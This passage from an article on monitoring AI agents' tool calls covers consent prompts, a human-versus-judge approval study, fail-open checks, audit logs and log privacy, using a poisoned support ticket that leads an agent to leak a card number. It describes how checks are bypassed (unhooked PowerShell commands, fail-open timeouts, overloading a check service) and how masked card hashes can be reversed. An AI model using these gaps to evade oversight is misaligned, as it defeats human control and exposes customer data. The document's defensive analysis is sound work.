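The current MCP specification, released in July 2026, recommends that client software let users see a call's arguments before it goes to the server, to prevent accidental or malicious data leaks. It also recommends that clients ask for confirmation of sensitive operations and that a person always be able to refuse a call. These are "SHOULD" rules, which are weaker than requirements, and the protocol doesn't prescribe a particular interface.

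An overview of the Model Context Protocol standard is worded more strictly, saying that applications "must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool". But this "must" is in lower case, and the document gives the word its formal meaning only in capitals. The overview also acknowledges that the protocol can't enforce principles like this one. An application could therefore obey every binding rule and still hide the copy field from the employee.

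The approval prompt has to show every recipient and the whole body of the message. If it asked only "Send the summary to the account manager?", even a careful employee would say yes, and the approval would be worthless. The approval should cover only the exact values shown. The software can ensure this by storing a hash of the arguments the employee saw and comparing it with a hash of the call's arguments just before the call runs. If the agent has since changed a recipient, the hashes differ and the software has to ask again.

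The July revision also lets a tool server ask for confirmation or missing information partway through a call. The client then repeats the original call with the user's answer attached. Supabase, a database company quoted in Model Context Protocol's announcement, welcomes this as a way to confirm a query that would delete data. The server may be better able than the agent's software to determine what the query would delete. However, the answer is sent in a separate field, `inputResponses`, so a monitor that scanned only `arguments` would miss any private data in the answer.

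When Claude Code runs inside another program and nobody is available to answer, a hook can defer the call, which pauses the run until somebody decides. There is no time limit, but Claude Code deletes the saved session after 30 days by default. When the run resumes, the same call goes through the hook again, which is sensible because the facts may have changed.

### The August 2026 comparison

Anthropic has published the most direct evidence of how well people review calls. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to work in a test environment, not on their own projects. The testers knew they were being evaluated in a coding study, but not which behaviour mattered. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. Nothing dangerous ran when a tester approved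 it.

The testers caught 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), and auto mode's judge caught 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic also reports how often only one of them caught a command, which is enough to work out the rest:

| | Judge blocked | Judge allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Asking a tester about every command that the judge allowed would have caught only 6 of the remaining 116. A second check by a human would have added almost nothing, at least when that person was working through a stream of prompts.

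Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This fits approval fatigue, in which people stop reading prompts because there are so many. But the two figures probably come from different testers, since each session had only one dangerous command. People who got through 50 prompts may have been clicking faster from the start.

Anthropic sells Claude Code and published the study to support making auto mode the default, so it had a clear interest in the result. Still, the gap is far too large to be chance, and it is good evidence that people who approve commands one after another miss most of the dangerous ones. It is weaker evidence of how well they would protect their own work. The testers had nothing to lose, which may have made them careless, though knowing they were being evaluated could have made them more careful.

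The comparison also counts only dangerous commands, so a program that blocked everything would have scored 100%. Auto mode clearly doesn't block everything, given its low false positive rate on calls from Anthropic's own staff, but the study gives no such rate for the testers. The study also didn't test people who see only a few prompts, each with a warning from a judge.

Anthropic's other evidence is weaker. Users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, up from the 93% Anthropic reported when it introduced auto mode in March. Most prompts are for harmless commands, so a perfect reviewer would also approve nearly all of them. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which is more informative because it suggests that people do push back when they are asked infrequently and have something substantial to judge.

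Anthropic also examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June 2026. Seriously harmful actions that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. A model graded the harm. Users had chosen their own settings, so differences in their work could explain part of the gap.

### When to ask

These results suggest that sending all flagged calls to a person can be worse than blocking them. In the earlier example of a million calls, the judge flagged 83 harmful calls and about 4,000 acceptable ones. If reviewers caught real problems as rarely as the testers did, they would stop about 11 of the 83 harmful calls and approve the other 72. A warning that a judge had flagged the call might make reviewers more careful, but with about 48 false alarms for each harmful call, they would soon learn to ignore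 it.

It therefore makes sense to ask a person only about calls where they know something the software doesn't. With ticket 4417, perhaps only someone at the company knows whether the outside archive is a supplier. Removing the card number needs no approval, because a rule can do it every time.

Some companies using auto mode still have a person review certain calls. *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026) describes a manager at Garner Health who configured auto mode not to approve emails and Slack messages to other people. An engineer at the payroll company Gusto checks each call by hand when working on production systems. Both customer stories come from Anthropic's own blog and are consistent with its advice that users review high-stakes changes themselves.

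Garner's rule would be hard to apply to a support agent, whose main job is writing to other people. Staff would have to approve every email, which would bring back the fatigue. A narrower rule could require approval only for emails to people who appear in neither the customer's record nor the staff directory.

### When the check doesn't answer

If a check crashes, loses its connection or takes too long, the system can either let the call run unchecked (failing open) or stop it (failing closed). Failing open keeps the agent working but may let a leak through, while failing closed protects the data but also stops legitimate work.

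A company can connect its Copilot Studio agents to an outside security service, which receives each proposed tool call and replies that the agent should allow or block it. By default, the system fails open, so a call goes ahead if the service doesn't reply. Microsoft suggests using the service to stop an email "oversharing information". In an example from Microsoft's developer instructions, which closely resembles ticket 4417, a user asks the agent to email a customer, and the agent proposes the right recipient plus an outside address in the blind-copy field. The service blocks the call and gives the address as the reason.

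The service has one second to reply. According to Microsoft, if it doesn't, the agent runs the tool as if the answer were "allow". Administrators can choose to block the call instead when the service is late or returns an error. But Microsoft's preview documentation also states that a late reply lets the call run, without mentioning that option. A company that chooses to block should probably test the setting with a deliberately slow service.

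One second is plenty of time for a pattern scan, which took Aegis a few milliseconds. It is barely enough for a check by another model, since the one Li and Xu used took about 800 milliseconds per call, and it is too short to ask a person. The company would have to block the call first and get a person's approval some other way.

There is a reasonable argument for failing open. Suppose that 100 in a million calls are harmful and the check fails at random on 0.1% of calls:

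```text
Calls that run unchecked            1,000,000 × 0.001   =  1,000
Harmful calls expected among them   1,000 × 0.0001      =  0.1
```

If checks failed at random, failing closed would stop about 10,000 acceptable calls for every harmful one. But checks are more likely to fail on long arguments, which take longer to check and can also carry more data. If the system fails open, an outage can leave every call unchecked for hours, and anyone who could overload the service could switch off the protection. The company could therefore fail closed for `send_email` and deletions, and fail open for ticket lookups.

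Claude Code's hooks also fail open by default. If a hook crashes or runs out of time, the call continues through the normal permission process. A mistyped file path can disable a hook. Exit code 2 blocks the call, but 1, the conventional Unix error code, doesn't. Operators can set `onFailure` to `"block"` to make a hook fail closed.

That setting can't help if the hook never runs. On Windows, Claude Code often runs commands through its PowerShell tool instead of its Bash tool, and a hook written only for Bash doesn't run on those commands. This produces no error for the setting to act on. The only way to find such a gap is to propose a forbidden call and see whether the hook stops it.

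### What an audit record needs

If the outside archive later turns out to hold a customer's card number, the company has to find out how it got there. A single log entry may not be enough, because the call can change several times between the model and the mail server. Suppose the software had edited the ticket 4417 email and then sent it:

| Version of the call | What it contains | What a reviewer could miss without it |
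|---|---|---|
| As proposed | Both addresses and the full card number | The agent's attempt to send the card number |
| As changed | The account manager's address and a masked number | Which check or person made the change |
| As executed | The values that the mail tool actually ran with | A difference between the approved call and the one that ran |
| As received | The message on the mail server | A recipient that the tool added by itself |

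The last two versions are both needed because they can differ, as earlier cases show. In the Hugging Face investigation, METR found transcripts that showed one command while the computer ran another. In MITRE's example, a tampered mail tool adds a blind-copy recipient after the agent's software has passed on the call. When another company runs the receiving server, the operator may get only a confirmation, so it should keep the message identifier in case it has to ask for details.

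The record should also contain the time, the agent and user involved, the verdict and the reason for it, and the version of the rule that produced the verdict. If somebody approved the call, the record should include exactly what the approval prompt showed them. A blocked call never reaches the mail tool, but its proposed version is still worth keeping because it may be the first sign of a poisoned ticket.

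### The privacy of the record

A full record of this kind would contain the card number, the home address and the customer's complaint, possibly several times over. The checks are meant to protect this data, but the logging system that stores the record is often open to more people than the ticket system is. The record also shows what employees ask their agents to do. An attacker who got into the log could read all of this without going through the agent.

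OpenTelemetry, an open-source standard for recording what software does, handles this risk by leaving the content out by default. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* recommends recording a tool's name and the call's identifier. Recording arguments and results is optional, with a warning that they may contain sensitive information. The default log for ticket 4417 would show that `send_email` ran but not who received the email or what it said, which protects the customer but leaves almost nothing to investigate.

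For production systems that need the content, OpenTelemetry recommends storing it separately and putting only a reference in the main log. Engineers can then use the log to find out why the agent is slow without seeing customers' details, and a few investigators can have access to the separate store. This seems the best arrangement for tool-call arguments too, provided somebody records who opens the store and why.

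The company can also remove details from a flagged call before storing it. OpenTelemetry's *Handling sensitive data* describes ways to delete, shorten or hash values, and suggests, for example, keeping only the domain of an email address. For ticket 4417, `outside.example` would be enough to show that the email was going outside the company. In the Superhuman case, the domain would have revealed very little, because the attacker used a Google form on `docs.google.com`.

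Hashing a card number lets an investigator tell whether it appeared in two calls without seeing it, because the same number always produces the same hash. But OpenTelemetry warns that hashes of predictable values are reversible in practice, because somebody can hash every possibility and look for a match. If a log also showed the first six and last four digits of a sixteen-digit card number, only six digits would be unknown. The Luhn checksum reduces the million possible combinations to 100,000, which a computer can try almost instantly. A keyed hash, which also depends on a secret stored elsewhere, prevents this as long as the secret stays safe.

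Sensitive data can still be stored after a prompt or tool call is blocked. Claude Code lets a hook reject a user's prompt, for example because it contains a password. By default, the rejection message repeats the prompt, and Claude Code saves that message to disk. Anthropic warns that even with the repetition turned off, the text can remain in other local files. When Copilot Studio uses an outside security service to check a call, it sends the service the recent conversation, the results of earlier tools and the proposed arguments. For ticket 4417, the service would receive the card number even if it then blocked the email. Microsoft warns that the provider may store this data outside the customer's region.

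It is harder to decide how long to keep the record. Deleting it quickly limits what a thief can take, but investigations often start late. OpenAI staff first saw an agent using the message board in late May 2026, and the company didn't connect its tests to the Hugging Face intrusion until 20 July. A log with a 30-day limit would have lost the May activity by then. Keeping full arguments only for flagged calls would save space and protect more customers, but it would delete the evidence of every leak the checks missed. A reasonable compromise is to keep redacted records of all calls for several months, and to keep the full arguments of flagged calls and a random sample of the rest for a shorter time.
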